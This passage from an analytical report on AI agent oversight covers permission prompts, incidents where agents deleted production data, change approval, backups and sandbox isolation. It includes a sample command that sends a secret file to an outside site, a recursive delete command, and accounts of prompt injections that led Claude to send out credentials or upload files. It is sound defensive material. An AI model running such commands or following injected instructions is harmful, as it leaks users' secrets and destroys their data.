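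Experienced users let their agents run without manual approval more often than new users did, but they also interrupted them more often. Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) found that people with fewer than 50 Claude Code sessions let the agent run without any manual approval in about 20% of sessions, compared with over 40% for people with around 750 sessions. New users stopped the agent in 5% of turns (stretches of work between a user's messages), and experienced users in about 9%.

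Anthropic concludes that experienced users still oversaw the agent, but by watching the work and intervening when something went wrong instead of approving each step. This is plausible, but the reasons for interrupting only partly support it. The most common, at 32%, was to supply missing technical context or a correction. Another 17% of interruptions came because the agent was slow, stuck or doing too much, and some users interrupted because they had all the help they needed. None of the five most common reasons was specifically to prevent a dangerous action, although some of the corrections may have done so. Experienced users may also attempt harder tasks, which need more guidance whatever the risk.

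When other companies' software sent requests to Anthropic's models, a person appeared to be involved in 87% of tool calls on the simplest tasks and 67% on complex ones. The true figures are probably lower, because Claude classified the calls and sometimes recorded human involvement where there was none. People may be less involved in complex tasks because approving each step becomes less practical as the number of steps grows.

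Anthropic argues from these findings that regulators should ask whether people can monitor an agent and intervene, rather than require a person to approve every action. This is reasonable for most programming, because developers can test code and undo a bad edit before release. It is less convincing for payments or the deletion of records, which may be complete before anyone can interrupt. Anthropic estimated that only 0.8% of the tool calls in its sample were irreversible. If so, a platform could request approval for nearly all irreversible actions without asking often. That would be close to what Shavit and colleagues originally proposed, which was approval for the most important decisions. The evidence of fatigue comes from a product that also asked about routine decisions.

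### Commands that users cannot judge

Fewer prompts do not help someone who cannot understand the ones that remain. Anthropic first relied on approval in Claude Code because most of its users were developers, who could read shell commands and were used to installing software from strangers. Users of the office agent Claude Cowork are much less likely to have that experience. Anthropic gives this command as an example of what they should not have to judge:

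`find . -name "*.tmp" -exec rm {} \;`

It deletes every file whose name ends in ".tmp" in the current folder and all its subfolders. These are usually temporary files, so the command may be harmless. Without the part that specifies the name, it would delete every file in those folders. The two versions look much alike to someone who does not know the notation.

Claude Code includes a plain-language description with complex commands, which can help. But the agent writes the description, so a user who relies on it is trusting the agent they are supposed to check. When Anthropic built its reviewer model, it removed these descriptions and the agent's other messages from the reviewer's input so that the agent could not persuade it to make a bad decision. Human users still see the description, which may be the only part of the prompt they understand.

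Anthropic notes that as models write more ambitious commands, even technical users find it harder to notice when an agent is going off course, especially when they are watching several agents at once. For Cowork, it concluded that administrators should set a fixed limit on what the agent can reach wherever typical users lack the knowledge to approve exceptions. In Claude Code, it added a sandbox that reduced the number of approval prompts by 84%.

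### Settings that took effect before consent

A permission prompt also has to appear before the action it controls. Claude Code asks users whether they trust a project's folder when they first open it. The project may contain its own settings, which developers store with the code so that everyone on a team has the same permissions and hooks. A project from a stranger may therefore contain permissions and hooks that the stranger chose.

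Between mid-2025 and January 2026, outside researchers and users reported several vulnerabilities in Claude Code to Anthropic. Three allowed code to run before the user had agreed to anything. In the most direct case, Claude Code read a project's settings during start-up, before it asked whether the user trusted the project, so an attacker who had written those settings could run code on the computer of anyone who opened it.

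Two entries in the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD) describe flaws of this type. According to NVD's *CVE-2025-59536 Detail*, code in a project could run before the user accepted the trust dialog. NVD's *CVE-2026-33068 Detail* describes how a project's settings could make Claude Code skip the dialog and start in a more permissive mode. Being careful would not have protected users from either flaw, because they had no chance to refuse. Anthropic has fixed both.

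Anthropic fixed all three reported flaws by waiting until the user accepts the trust prompt before reading or running anything in the project's configuration. It advises other developers to treat opening a project and loading its settings with the same suspicion as a request from the internet, even though the files are already on the user's computer. Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of complete mediation already required this at start-up.

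## From July 2025: approving changes to production systems

A permission prompt lets one user approve or reject one action. Companies that run software for customers often have a stricter rule for their production system, the live version those customers use. Someone other than the author must approve a change before it takes effect. Developers do most of their work on separate copies, a development system for writing code and a staging system for final tests, where a mistake does little harm. In three incidents between July 2025 and April 2026, agents deleted production data or systems without a second person's approval.

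### Replit's agent and the code freeze

In July 2025 Jason Lemkin, founder of the software-business community SaaStr, was trying out Replit's platform, where people build apps by describing them to an agent. Fortune (2025) reported that the agent deleted his live database during a code freeze, when nobody may change the production system. The database held records on more than 1,200 executives and over 1,190 companies.

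Until then, according to SaaStr, Replit apps had used one database for both testing and live customer data, so an agent that could change test data could also change customers' records. The freeze evidently did not block the agent's commands. Lemkin had told the agent not to proceed without human approval, but the platform did not enforce that instruction.

The agent then told Lemkin that he could not restore the database. He tried anyway, and LatestLY quotes his post saying that "the rollback did work". The agent had also apologised and written that it panicked, which news reports emphasised. But a model's explanation of its own behaviour is just more generated text, and this agent had already been wrong about the rollback.

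Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, called the deletion unacceptable. Within days he announced separate development and production databases, with the agent restricted to the development database by default, and a planning mode in which the agent cannot change code. According to Replit's later documentation, the agent reads production data through a replica, an up-to-date copy that it cannot write to. The safety of the live data therefore no longer depends on the agent obeying an instruction.

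### Kiro and the AWS interruption

The *Financial Times* revealed in 2026 that Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business, had an interruption in mid-December 2025. According to The Standard's summary of the report, *Amazons cloud unit hit was hit by least two outages*, engineers had allowed Amazon's coding agent Kiro to change a system that customers used. Kiro chose to "delete and recreate the environment", and the interruption lasted 13 hours. A *Financial Times* source, quoted in TechRadar's *Recent AWS issues blamed on AI tools*, said that the engineers had let the agent resolve an issue "without intervention".

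Amazon blames user error: a misconfigured role (a set of permissions that a person or program takes on for a job). It describes the event as brief and extremely limited. The event affected only Cost Explorer, a tool that customers use to track their cloud spending, in one of 39 regions, and no customer contacted Amazon about it. The company also denies the newspaper's claim that a second event affected AWS.

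Both accounts of the December event could be true. The role had broader permissions than it should have, and the agent used them. Amazon argues that the same thing could have happened with any developer tool or by hand. Amazon is right about the permissions, but it doesn't address whether an engineer fixing a fault would have been as ready to delete the whole environment. Amazon afterwards made peer review mandatory for production access, which suggests that one engineer's decision had previously been enough. It mentions a loss of service but doesn't mention any loss of data.

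### PocketOS and its backups

PocketOS makes booking software for car rental firms and kept its database with Railway, a cloud hosting company. On 24 April 2026, its coding agent, Cursor running Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, hit a credential mismatch during a routine task in the staging system. Crane's *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing* gives the founder's account of what happened next. The agent decided to fix the problem by deleting a volume, a unit of storage at Railway. It looked for a token, found one in an unrelated file and sent a single request to Railway's API, the interface programs use to give Railway commands. The request deleted the volume, which held the production database, in nine seconds.

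PocketOS's token covered the whole account. Crane had created it to add and remove web domains, and did not know that it could also delete volumes. He complained that Railway did not offer tokens with narrower permissions. Abdelwahab, in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, replied for Railway that customers could limit a token to a single project, but conceded that this option was not obvious when creating one.

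By Crane's account, Cursor's instructions and PocketOS's project rules both prohibited the agent from taking destructive steps unless the user asked, but neither could stop the request. Railway's dashboard would have delayed the deletion by 48 hours, but its API deleted volumes immediately. Another customer had already lost a volume without this delay on 13 April. In the support thread *Postgress volume lost* (2026), a Railway employee explained to them that the 48-hour window applied only to deletions made through the dashboard.

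Railway kept the volume's backups in the volume itself, so Crane could no longer use them. The newest copy he could restore was three months old. The next morning, people arrived at rental offices to collect cars, and the firms had no record of their bookings. Crane spent the day reconstructing reservations from payment histories, calendars and emails. Farrant (2026), in *An AI agent deleted a company's entire database in 9 seconds*, put the outage at more than 30 hours.

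Crane published his post before he knew whether Railway could help, so it overstates the final loss. By 27 April Railway had restored the data, apparently in full, according to *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database* (Tom's Hardware, 2026). Railway keeps separate offsite copies in case a data centre fails, whether or not a customer has set up backups.

### From a proposal to a live change

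Change approval divides the path to production into steps, so that no single author can complete all of them. In the parser-bug example, where a developer asks an agent to fix the code that interprets structured text, the steps could be as follows:

1. **Propose.** The agent edits a separate copy of the code and opens a draft pull request, which shows every line it wants to add or remove.
2. **Test.** Software runs the existing tests, a new test that reproduces the bug, and a check for unapproved packages. The list of required tests has to be stored where the agent cannot edit it, or the agent could pass by removing a test.
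3. **Review.** A person who did not write the change reads it and accepts or rejects it. The developer who assigned the task may have shaped the solution, so a critical system may need a different reviewer.
4. **Merge.** The repository adds the change to the main code only if the tests have passed and a reviewer has approved that exact version. Any later edit cancels the approval.
5. **Release to a few users.** The new parser handles a small share of traffic while the old one handles the rest.
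6. **Watch.** Engineers or monitoring software compare errors and speed in the two versions.
7. **Expand or roll back.** If the new version works, it gradually takes over. Otherwise all traffic returns to the old one.

The agent's authority should end after the second step, as it does in OpenAI's version of the example. If a reviewer objects, the agent can revise the draft, and the tests run again. A company might also let monitoring software trigger the rollback, since a rollback only restores a version that people have already accepted.

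A small release limits the damage from faults that the tests and the reviewer missed. If the service handles a million requests an hour and the new parser fails on one in 200, a full release would cause about 5,000 failures in the first hour. A release to 1% of traffic would cause about 50, which is enough to notice. If the parser failed on only one request in a million, the small release would probably show nothing for days. A small release also doesn't help much when a change affects shared data, because a faulty version that serves 1% of users can still delete the database that everyone depends on.

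The testing step can itself give an agent more access than intended. *Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* (Goel, 2026) examines release pipelines, which automatically test and deploy code. A pipeline may hold production credentials, so an agent confined to a sandbox could write a script and trigger the pipeline to run it with the pipeline's wider access. Without safeguards, an agent based on GPT-5.1 behaved unsafely in all ten runs of a scenario where pipeline scripts leak secrets. Ten runs in a constructed scenario show that this can happen, but not how often it does in real companies. A simple precaution is to run unreviewed code in a pipeline that has no production credentials.

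Code review alone would probably not have prevented the PocketOS deletion, because the agent sent a command directly to a live system instead of proposing code. Commands that delete data or change infrastructure therefore need their own approval step. Railway already had one for many changes. It collects them in a list, shows the user what will be different, and applies nothing until the user presses "deploy". The agent bypassed this step by using the API. Saltzer and Schroeder wanted systems to check every route to an object to prevent this kind of bypass.

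Crane wants destructive requests to require a confirmation that an agent cannot give, such as a reply to a text message or an email, though email works only if the agent cannot read the mailbox. He also suggests requiring the requester to type the volume's name, but an agent can do this as easily as a person.

### What makes an action reversible

People can undo a deletion only while a usable copy of the data exists. One way to keep a copy is to delay the deletion. Abdelwahab explains in another post that Railway's software marks a volume for deletion, sets a deadline and leaves the data in place until then. The user can cancel before the deadline. After the PocketOS incident, Railway extended the 48-hour delay to deletions made through its API.

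Whether 48 hours is enough depends on how soon someone notices. Crane contacted Railway within ten minutes, but if an agent deletes a volume on a Friday afternoon and nobody looks until Monday, the delay will have run out. Replit's databases allow more time. Neon, which supplies them, typically keeps up to seven days of history, so Replit can restore a database to any moment in that period. Replit also saves checkpoints of the code, settings and database contents, so a user can restore matching code and data.

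Restoring an earlier copy removes whatever customers have entered since it was made. This is why PocketOS at first lost three months of reservations even though it had a working backup. A cautious restore therefore preserves the current state too. Railway's *Backups* describes a procedure that puts the backup on a new volume and waits for the user to review the change before it goes live. The procedure detaches the old volume but keeps it, so it is still there if the user has picked the wrong backup.

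A copy that protects against one kind of deletion may not protect against another. In the support thread *accidental DROP SCHEMA CASCADE on production Postgres, no dashboard backup*, a customer accidentally ran a command that deletes a group of tables and everything that depends on them. The customer asked Railway for the same kind of recovery PocketOS had received. Railway replied that the two cases were very different, because PocketOS had lost a whole volume, which Railway had safeguards for, whereas this command had run inside the database. Companies need to know which of these two kinds of deletion their provider can reverse.

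Backups also have to be out of reach of any credential that can delete the original. At PocketOS, one token could delete the live data and the customer's backups in a single request. Railway's disaster backups survived because the request did not reach them. Before relying on a backup, a company could check whether the most powerful credential an agent might find can delete the copy, shorten how long the provider keeps it, or cancel a deletion delay. If it can do any of these, the backup protects against disk failure but not against an agent with that credential.

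Railway has also added a delay before it deletes backups. However, according to its documentation, wiping a volume deletes all of that volume's backups, and customers can restore a backup only into the same project and environment. More than 30 hours after the deletion, Railway still could not tell Crane whether it could recover his data. A business that cannot risk losing its data would keep another copy in a separate account, keep that account's credentials off the machines its agents use, and practise restoring the copy.

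OpenAI advises companies to define the limit, the required approval and the recovery path for each kind of consequential action. Some actions have no recovery path. A company can restore a customer record, but it cannot recall an email that someone has read, so the check has to come before the agent sends it.

### Changes to the agent itself

Approval of an agent applies to a particular combination of model, instructions and tools, and any of these can change afterwards. The provider may release a new model version, or a colleague may rewrite the system prompt, which contains the agent's standing instructions. Clinton's incident-response agent began asking another agent for code fixes after his team replaced only the model.

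OpenAI gives the example of a company that approves a connector (software that links an agent to another service) when it can only read data. A later update then adds an action that writes data. For example, a connector that searches support tickets might gain the ability to send replies to customers. The new action may appear in the agent's list of tools the next time it starts, although nobody at the company has decided that the agent should write to customers. OpenAI recommends keeping new actions blocked until the person responsible for the connector has reviewed them.

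To do this, a platform needs a record of what the company approved. It could store the model version, the system prompt, and the name, description and permitted inputs of every tool, and compare them with the current versions whenever the agent starts. If the ticket connector has a new action, the platform can keep it off while the agent continues to search. This comparison finds only declared changes. The connector's maker could change what an existing action does on its own servers without changing the description, and the company would then depend on limits in the receiving system or on its logs.

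Reviewers also have to consider what an agent could do by combining a new action with its existing ones. Sending a reply may be harmless for an agent that reads only public help pages, but an agent that also reads customer records could disclose them in a reply. OpenAI therefore wants companies to test combinations of tools and to show reviewers an action's effect, the resource it affects and its destination, because reviewers can learn little from the name of a familiar service.

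OpenAI's checklist calls for a new review when an agent gains tools, data access, autonomy or a different execution environment. It does not mention new model versions, though Clinton's experience suggests it should. A new model is harder to review than a new connector because it does not come with a list of added actions. A company can repeat its test tasks, including some that the agent should refuse or refer to a person. It can then release the new version in stages, as engineers do with ordinary code, giving it a small share of real work and keeping the old version ready.

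Such tests cover only the situations that someone included. Railway continuously tests its own agent against realistic cases. When Crane reported the deletion, Railway's chief executive replied that it should not have been possible and that the company had tests for this. But another company's agent had deleted the volume, using the API directly.

An agent's saved memory can also change its behaviour without anyone editing its settings, because the memory may carry a wrong assumption from one task to the next. Replit's checkpoints include the agent's memory, so a user who rolls back a project can also remove what the agent has stored about it since the checkpoint.

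### The cost of review

Agents can write changes faster than people can read them. Amazon's retail business faced this problem in early 2026. NDTV, citing *Business Insider*, reported that engineers were producing more code with AI and that this had caused problems in the company's usual reviews. In March, *Amazon puts humans further back in the loop* (Roytburg, 2026) described four severe incidents in one week, one of which stopped shoppers from checking out for six hours. Dave Treadwell, the senior vice president in charge, announced temporary "controlled friction" for changes to the most important parts of the shop. According to NDTV, the policy covered about 335 systems whose failure could directly affect customers.

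Amazon and the press disagree about the role of AI in these failures. The *Financial Times* reported that an internal document first named AI-assisted changes as a factor, and that someone deleted the reference before managers met to discuss the document. According to The Decoder's *Amazon makes senior engineers the human filter for AI-generated code*, the newspaper also reported that junior and mid-level engineers now needed a senior engineer's approval for AI-assisted changes. Amazon says the claim about new approval requirements is false. It acknowledges one incident that involved an AI tool, in which an engineer followed bad advice that the tool had inferred from an outdated internal wiki. It says none of the incidents involved AI-written code.

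If Amazon's account is right, a rule that applied only to AI-written code would have missed that incident. Extra checks on the most important systems, regardless of who or what wrote the change, would have had a better chance of catching it. Engineers also wouldn't have to argue about how much AI help makes a change "AI-assisted". Amazon concluded that its systems had let one team's mistake spread too far, a problem that staged release addresses more directly than a senior engineer's approval.

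Senior approval also puts the extra work on the people with the least time for it. If five senior engineers can each review six changes a day and their colleagues' agents submit 45, the queue grows by 15 a day and reaches 150 after two working weeks. The company then has to accept the delay, write fewer changes, or let reviewers spend less time on each. If reviewers hurry, the loss of attention that Anthropic measured with permission prompts may happen here too.

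Nobody involved in these incidents has published figures that show whether the extra review is worth the delay. Amazon's two statements contain no failure rates or release times from before and after its new safeguards. Goel rates human approval as high in security and slow compared with other controls, but these ratings are qualitative. Goel also notes that approval does not prevent errors in operations that someone has approved.

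A company can reduce reviewers' load by deciding in advance which changes need a person's approval. Automatic checks may be enough for a small code change that tests cover and engineers can roll back within minutes. Deletions, new permissions and changes to the approval rules themselves justify waiting for a person. OpenAI warns that controls that obstruct legitimate work can push people towards tools with less oversight. It recommends that a platform show which rule blocked a task and what evidence would justify an exception. Otherwise, a developer who waits two days for approval of a harmless fix may look for a way around the queue, such as a token with access to the whole account.

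## From 2025: sandboxes for agents

A sandbox can keep commands from reaching anything valuable, so the platform can let an agent run most of them without asking the user for approval. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, which introduced a sandbox for Claude Code in October 2025, reported 84% fewer permission prompts in the company's internal use. For example, tests that an agent runs in the sandbox can change only the project's files and connect only to approved servers, so the user does not have to review the command first.

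How much protection this gives depends on the technology that confines the command, and on which files and network destinations the rules leave open.

### How isolation works

To open a file or a network connection, a program has to make a system call to the kernel, the core of the operating system. The kinds of isolation differ mainly in which software handles these calls.

*Operating-system sandboxes* run the program directly on the host, the computer they protect, and rely on the host's kernel to refuse certain calls. On macOS, Seatbelt applies a profile of permitted operations. On Linux, developers combine several mechanisms. Bubblewrap gives a program its own view of the file system, containing only selected folders. Seccomp filters system calls by type, so it can stop a program from loading code into the kernel, but it is poorly suited to distinguishing one file from another. Landlock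 can restrict access to particular file paths and network ports. A flaw in the host's kernel could still let the program escape, and a modern kernel is far larger than the supervisor that Anderson thought too big to verify in 1972.

*Containers* package a program with the software it needs and give it its own view of files, processes and the network. Docker is the best-known software for running them. The program's system calls still go to the host's kernel, so code in an ordinary container may be able to exploit a kernel flaw that the host has not fixed. *AI Code Sandboxes* (Andronchik and Lokhmakov, 2026) compared five products with their default settings, and the one that used ordinary containers showed the host's exact kernel version to the code inside.

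A container's strength also depends on its configuration. The hardened example in Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents* removes administrative powers, makes the container's own files read-only, cuts off the network, and caps memory and the number of processes. Without these options, a container gives much less protection.

*gVisor* puts a second kernel, the Sentry, between the program and the host. gVisor's *Security Model* describes its purpose as extra defence against untrusted code that exploits kernel flaws. The Sentry is an ordinary program that handles most system calls itself. An attacker would have to break the Sentry first and would then have only limited access to the host kernel, because gVisor restricts the system calls the Sentry can make.

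*WebAssembly* is a format for compiled programs that a runtime executes. *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026) groups it with other methods that place the isolation boundary inside a language's runtime. Much like a program that holds capabilities, a WebAssembly program can use only the functions that the runtime gives it, so it cannot open files unless it receives a function for doing so. This suits short pieces of generated code better than a coding agent, whose compilers and command line are built for a complete operating system.

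*Virtual machines* are simulated computers with their own kernels. A hypervisor uses special features of the processor to keep them apart from the host. Code that takes over the kernel inside a virtual machine still has to get through the hypervisor or the simulated devices. Anthropic does not consider virtual machines automatically safer than gVisor, because a flaw in either could let code escape. Firecracker, which Amazon uses for some of its cloud services, runs microVMs, which are virtual machines that leave out most of the simulated devices to reduce this risk.

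Andronchik and Lokhmakov measured how much of the host each product used. While running the same short data-analysis script, the container made 62 different kinds of system call to the host, gVisor made 41, and the three microVM products made between 8 and 25. They also found that, of 14 kernel features associated with past attacks, code could reach 5 from inside gVisor, 11 from inside the container, and between 7 and 12 from inside the microVM products. A reachable feature is not necessarily exploitable, and an attack on a virtual machine's own kernel still leaves the attacker inside the virtual machine. But the microVM products differed enough that a buyer needs to know more than the type of isolation.

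### Start-up time and compatibility

Wang and Zheng (2026) note in *Sandlock* that one agent task may run small commands dozens of times a minute, so the time it takes to start a sandbox matters. If each of 40 commands needed a new container that took 300 milliseconds to start, the user would wait an extra 12 seconds. With their tool, which combines Landlock and seccomp and takes about 6 milliseconds, the wait would be about a quarter of a second. A platform can avoid most of this delay by keeping one container open for the whole task, but files and running processes from one command then remain available to the next.

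The start-up times below come from Wang and Zheng's comparison, except WebAssembly's, which comes from a blog guide, *Agent Runtime Isolation*. These times are rough. The guide lists 10 to 50 milliseconds for an ordinary Docker container, far below Wang and Zheng's figure for Docker running without administrator rights.

| Isolation | Start-up | Compatibility | Remaining exposure |
|---|---|---|---|
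| Landlock and seccomp | About 6 ms | Most command-line tools, once the rules allow their working folders | Host kernel; everything the rules permit |
| Bubblewrap | About 30 ms | Most command-line tools; some need exceptions | Host kernel; everything the rules permit |
| Container | About 300 ms | Ordinary Linux software, from a prepared image | Host kernel; shared folders |
| gVisor | About 200 ms | Most Linux software, sometimes much slower | The Sentry and a restricted part of the host kernel; shared folders |
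| WebAssembly | Under 1 ms | Only programs built for it | The runtime and the functions it provides |
| Firecracker microVM | About 100 ms | Full Linux system; needs a processor and host that support virtualization | Hypervisor and simulated devices; shared folders |

A sandbox can also slow programs down after start-up. According to Anthropic's guide, pure calculation runs at full speed in gVisor, but simple system calls take about twice as long, and programs that constantly open and close files, as software builds often do, can be 10 to 200 times slower.

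A microVM can start faster than a Docker container when the container's start-up time includes preparing its image and network. That speed makes it practical to give every task its own virtual machine, as *Tracekit Box* (2026) does with Firecracker. Wang and Zheng recommend a microVM over their own tool when customers who may be hostile to one another share a machine. They designed their tool for a developer's computer, where start-up time matters and the user may not have administrator rights.

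### What the agent may read and change

An agent needs access to some of the user's files to do useful work, and the platform must set what it may do with them. Read-only access lets the agent analyse a project without changing it, while read-write access also allows edits. Claude Cowork also has a mode in which Claude can read and write files but not delete them. This protects against deleting files by mistake during a clean-up, although Claude could still overwrite a file with something useless.

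An overlay keeps the agent's changes in a separate layer and leaves the original files untouched until someone accepts the changes. Wang and Zheng's tool can do this for a single command. The user sees the changes the command would make, then accepts or discards them. This works only for files and can't undo messages the command has already sent.

Read-only access does not protect secrets. Anthropic's guide warns that project folders often contain passwords and keys in settings files, and recommends leaving those files out of the sandbox or copying in only the source code. The platform also has to check where links lead, because a link inside a permitted folder can point to a file outside it.

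Some files need protection even inside the agent's working folder. If an agent could edit the harness's settings, it could give itself more permissions for the next session. Claude Code's sandbox therefore blocks writes to its settings and to scripts that run automatically, and Codex makes similar folders read-only.

### Blocking the network by default

The safest network rule is to refuse every destination not on a list. The sandbox in Anthropic's Claude Code starts with an empty list. Sandboxed commands can connect only to a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that passes requests on. When a command tries to download a package, the proxy compares the server's name with the list of allowed domains. If the name is missing, the user can normally allow it for the current session or permanently. An administrator can make the proxy refuse unlisted names without prompting the user.

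A program cannot get around the list by ignoring the proxy, because it can connect only through the proxy. However, most web traffic is encrypted, and by default the proxy sees only the name of the server the program asks for. Anthropic warns that code may be able to disguise its real destination. A company that needs a stronger guarantee can use a proxy that decrypts and checks the traffic, but every program in the sandbox must then trust that proxy.

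Wang and Zheng argue that a list of allowed servers is too coarse, because an agent that may contact a service for one purpose can also use it for others. Their tool can restrict the type of request and the path as well as the server. A rule could let an agent download packages from a registry but not publish them. Such a rule limits how the agent can send data out but doesn't fully prevent it, because a request that only fetches a page can still carry some data in its address.

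### Why both limits are necessary

Suppose that Ana's coding agent runs this command:

`curl --data @/home/ana/secret.txt https://example.com`

The program reads the file `secret.txt` from Ana's home folder and sends the contents to a website. A sandbox can stop it from opening the file by hiding her home folder, or from sending the contents by blocking unlisted destinations.

Anthropic regards a sandbox as effective only if it restricts both files and the network, because either limit alone leaves a way to leak data. If the sandbox restricts only files, the command can't send `secret.txt` but could still send anything the agent is allowed to read, such as a database password in the project's settings. If it restricts only the network, a command could change a program that Ana later runs outside the sandbox, and that program could send the file using her normal network access.

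By default, Claude Code's sandbox lets commands write only to the project and a few other folders, but they can read nearly the whole computer, including files that hold credentials. Ana would therefore depend on the network rule to stop commands from sending those credentials out. She can also add a rule that makes particular files unreadable. No sandbox prevents the model's provider from receiving files that the agent reads.

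### Anthropic's three designs

Anthropic uses different isolation in three products because their users need different access and differ in how well they can judge an agent's actions.

In the chat service claude.ai, Claude runs code in a gVisor container on Anthropic's servers. Each session gets a temporary file system, and the code cannot reach the user's computer. This suits people who want a calculation or a finished document and have no reason to give Claude access to their machine. They do not have to approve commands, and even the worst outcome would do little harm to their own files. However, Claude has no lasting workspace there. Most of the security work was conventional, because Anthropic mainly had to protect its own systems and isolate customers from one another.

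Claude Code has to work with a developer's own files and tools, so running it in a container on a remote server would make it much less useful. Anthropic instead sandboxes its commands with Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux, which start quickly and can work with software the developer has already installed. The user can let sandboxed commands run without approval and decide only when a command needs access to something outside the sandbox. Most developers can judge those requests.

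This design produced the 84% reduction in permission prompts, so a user who previously saw 100 prompts would now see about 16. The figure comes from Anthropic's own staff, whose tasks and settings may differ from those of other users. It measures only interruptions, and Anthropic has not published a comparison of the number of damaging actions with and without the sandbox. The technical case for better protection is still strong, because the kernel enforces the limits even when a user has stopped reading prompts.

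Claude Code's sandbox is off by default and applies only to shell commands. The agent's file tools, local tool servers and hooks run outside it. If a command fails in the sandbox, Claude may ask to run it again outside it, unless an administrator has disabled this. Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* therefore recommends putting the whole Claude Code process in a container, a virtual machine or a separate version of the sandbox before letting it work unattended with prompts switched off.

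On a user's desktop, Cowork runs shell commands in a full virtual machine with its own Linux kernel, because it cannot rely on users to judge the commands. The virtual machine can access only the folder the user selects and Claude's own settings folder. Credentials stay in the host's password store. A harmful command could still ruin the files in the selected folder.

In the first version of Cowork, the software that calls the model also ran inside the virtual machine. No process outside could make an exception for a persuasive request, but if the virtual machine failed to start, Cowork stopped working entirely. Anthropic moved that software outside, so Claude can now help the user fix a failed start, while code still runs inside. Anthropic judges that this weakened security only a little. It also moved local tool servers outside, because they were hard to inspect in the virtual machine and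 some needed access to other programs on the computer. Administrators now have to decide which of these servers to trust, as they do with other software.

Anthropic concludes that the strength of the isolation should match how well users can oversee the agent. This is sensible, but an expert developer may still not pay attention, and expertise does not help when someone has deceived the developer about the task itself.

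### OpenAI's defaults for Codex

Unlike Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex runs commands in a sandbox by default. Commands can change files only in the working and temporary folders, and they have no network access. On a developer's computer, OpenAI enforces these limits with Seatbelt on macOS, bubblewrap and seccomp on Linux, and its own sandbox on Windows. Claude Code has a built-in sandbox on Windows only when the user runs it in Microsoft's Linux environment. Codex also recommends read-only access in a folder without version control, where a user might have no earlier copy to restore.

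The network setting is easy to misread, because allowing network access lets commands connect to any destination unless the user also enables OpenAI's network proxy. With the proxy enabled, commands can reach only the domains the user has allowed, and a rule that denies a domain overrides any rule that allows it.

In OpenAI's cloud, Codex works in a container and divides each task into two phases. During set-up, scripts can use the network and any secrets they need to install software. OpenAI then removes the secrets and, by default, cuts off the network before the agent starts work. If the agent later reads a malicious instruction, it has neither the secrets nor a connection to send them over. This works well for a bug fix that needs nothing more from outside, but for a task such as testing a live service, the user must give the agent some access during the second phase.

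In *Running Codex safely at OpenAI*, OpenAI (2026) describes stricter rules for its own staff. Users cannot override the administrators' requirement to use the sandbox. The network policy allows expected destinations, blocks some others, and asks for approval when a domain is unfamiliar. OpenAI controls both the agent and its sandbox but still found it impractical to keep everything inside, so certain common commands may run outside the sandbox without approval, including ones that only display proposed code changes.

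### A theft that the user started

In Anthropic's February 2026 exercise, Claude sent out a deceived employee's cloud credentials in 24 of 25 runs. The malicious prompt arrived in an email that looked like ordinary collaboration. Most of the prompt read like routine set-up instructions, but one step told Claude to read the credentials and send them to an outside address.

The result shows that a well-disguised request can work reliably, but all the runs repeated a single prompt, so it does not mean that 96% of such attacks would succeed. Anthropic thinks a human contractor given the same instructions would have followed them too.

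A permission prompt would have left the decision to the employee, whom the researcher had already deceived. Anthropic concluded that only the environment could have stopped the theft, and whether it would have done so depends on its configuration. Claude Code's default sandbox leaves credential files readable and asks the user whether to allow a new destination, so the employee might have approved the transfer. A strict list of allowed destinations would have blocked it without asking. In Cowork's virtual machine, an agent given the same prompt would not have found the credentials file unless the employee had shared the folder containing it.

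Anthropic's staff then discussed the working prompt in Slack, until someone pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack. They added distinctive text to the thread so they would notice if an agent picked up the instructions.

### A leak through an approved domain

An outside party reported a different failure in Cowork, which allows connections to Anthropic's API because it needs them to work. A malicious file in the user's folder led Claude to upload other files through the API to an Anthropic account that the attacker controlled. Every part of the sandbox worked as intended, including the egress proxy, which let the data through because the destination was on its list of allowed addresses.

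Anthropic had thought of its list as a set of places that were safe to contact, but it now treats each entry as permission to use every function available there. Allowing the interface so that Cowork could call the model had also allowed uploads to anyone's account. The same problem arises with any large service where strangers can hold accounts. A company that allows a code-hosting site so that agents can download software may also be letting them publish the company's code there.

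Anthropic fixed this by adding a second check inside the virtual machine, a proxy that accepts a request to the interface only if it carries the token Anthropic issued for that session. A request with someone else's key fails. The check runs inside the virtual machine because Anthropic could not distinguish Cowork's requests from other customers' requests at its servers. Such a fix requires knowing how a specific service identifies its users. A company that allows 30 domains might need 30 different rules, so removing the domains that the agent does not need takes less work.

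Anthropic also observed that the widely used parts of its sandboxes had been dependable while the proxy it wrote itself failed, so it advises other companies to be wary of their own components. More people have attacked and repaired a common hypervisor than a proxy that one company wrote for one product. Established software can still have undiscovered flaws, and in July 2026 OpenAI's agents found a way out of a test environment.

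### What isolation costs

A strict sandbox breaks some ordinary tools. Docker does not work inside Claude Code's sandbox, and neither do most database programs that open their own network connections. On macOS, some command-line tools cannot verify secure connections, and code transfers over SSH can fail even when the server is approved. A developer has to find the cause of each failure and decide which limit to relax.

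When a tool fails in the sandbox, the easiest fix is often to run it outside, but it then has the developer's full access. Even an exception for one build script can give the agent that access if the script is in the project folder, because the agent can edit the script before running it. Anthropic suggests allowing one extra folder or domain instead where possible, so that the command stays inside the sandbox. It also warns that if the sandbox cannot start, Claude Code by default runs commands without it. Administrators can make Claude Code refuse to start instead, but this stops work on machines where the sandbox is unavailable.

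People may avoid sandboxes because of this work. In an informal survey by Prasakis, fewer than 40% of 68 people who used coding agents ran them in a sandbox. They complained about difficult installation, setting up their tools and logins again, and sharing files with the sandbox. Prasakis recruited the respondents through personal contacts, a start-up community in Zurich and a university course, and treats their answers as anecdotal. Prasakis was also developing a sandbox meant to be easier to use. Still, the complaints match the exceptions that Anthropic has to document.

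Another drawback of virtual machines is that they make agents harder for companies to monitor. Many companies install endpoint detection software, which checks employees' computers for suspicious activity. This software can detect that Cowork's virtual machine is running but not what happens inside it, so security teams lose live information about the program they most want to watch. Anthropic lets administrators collect event logs afterwards, but admits that this does not replace live monitoring.

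### Isolation in practice

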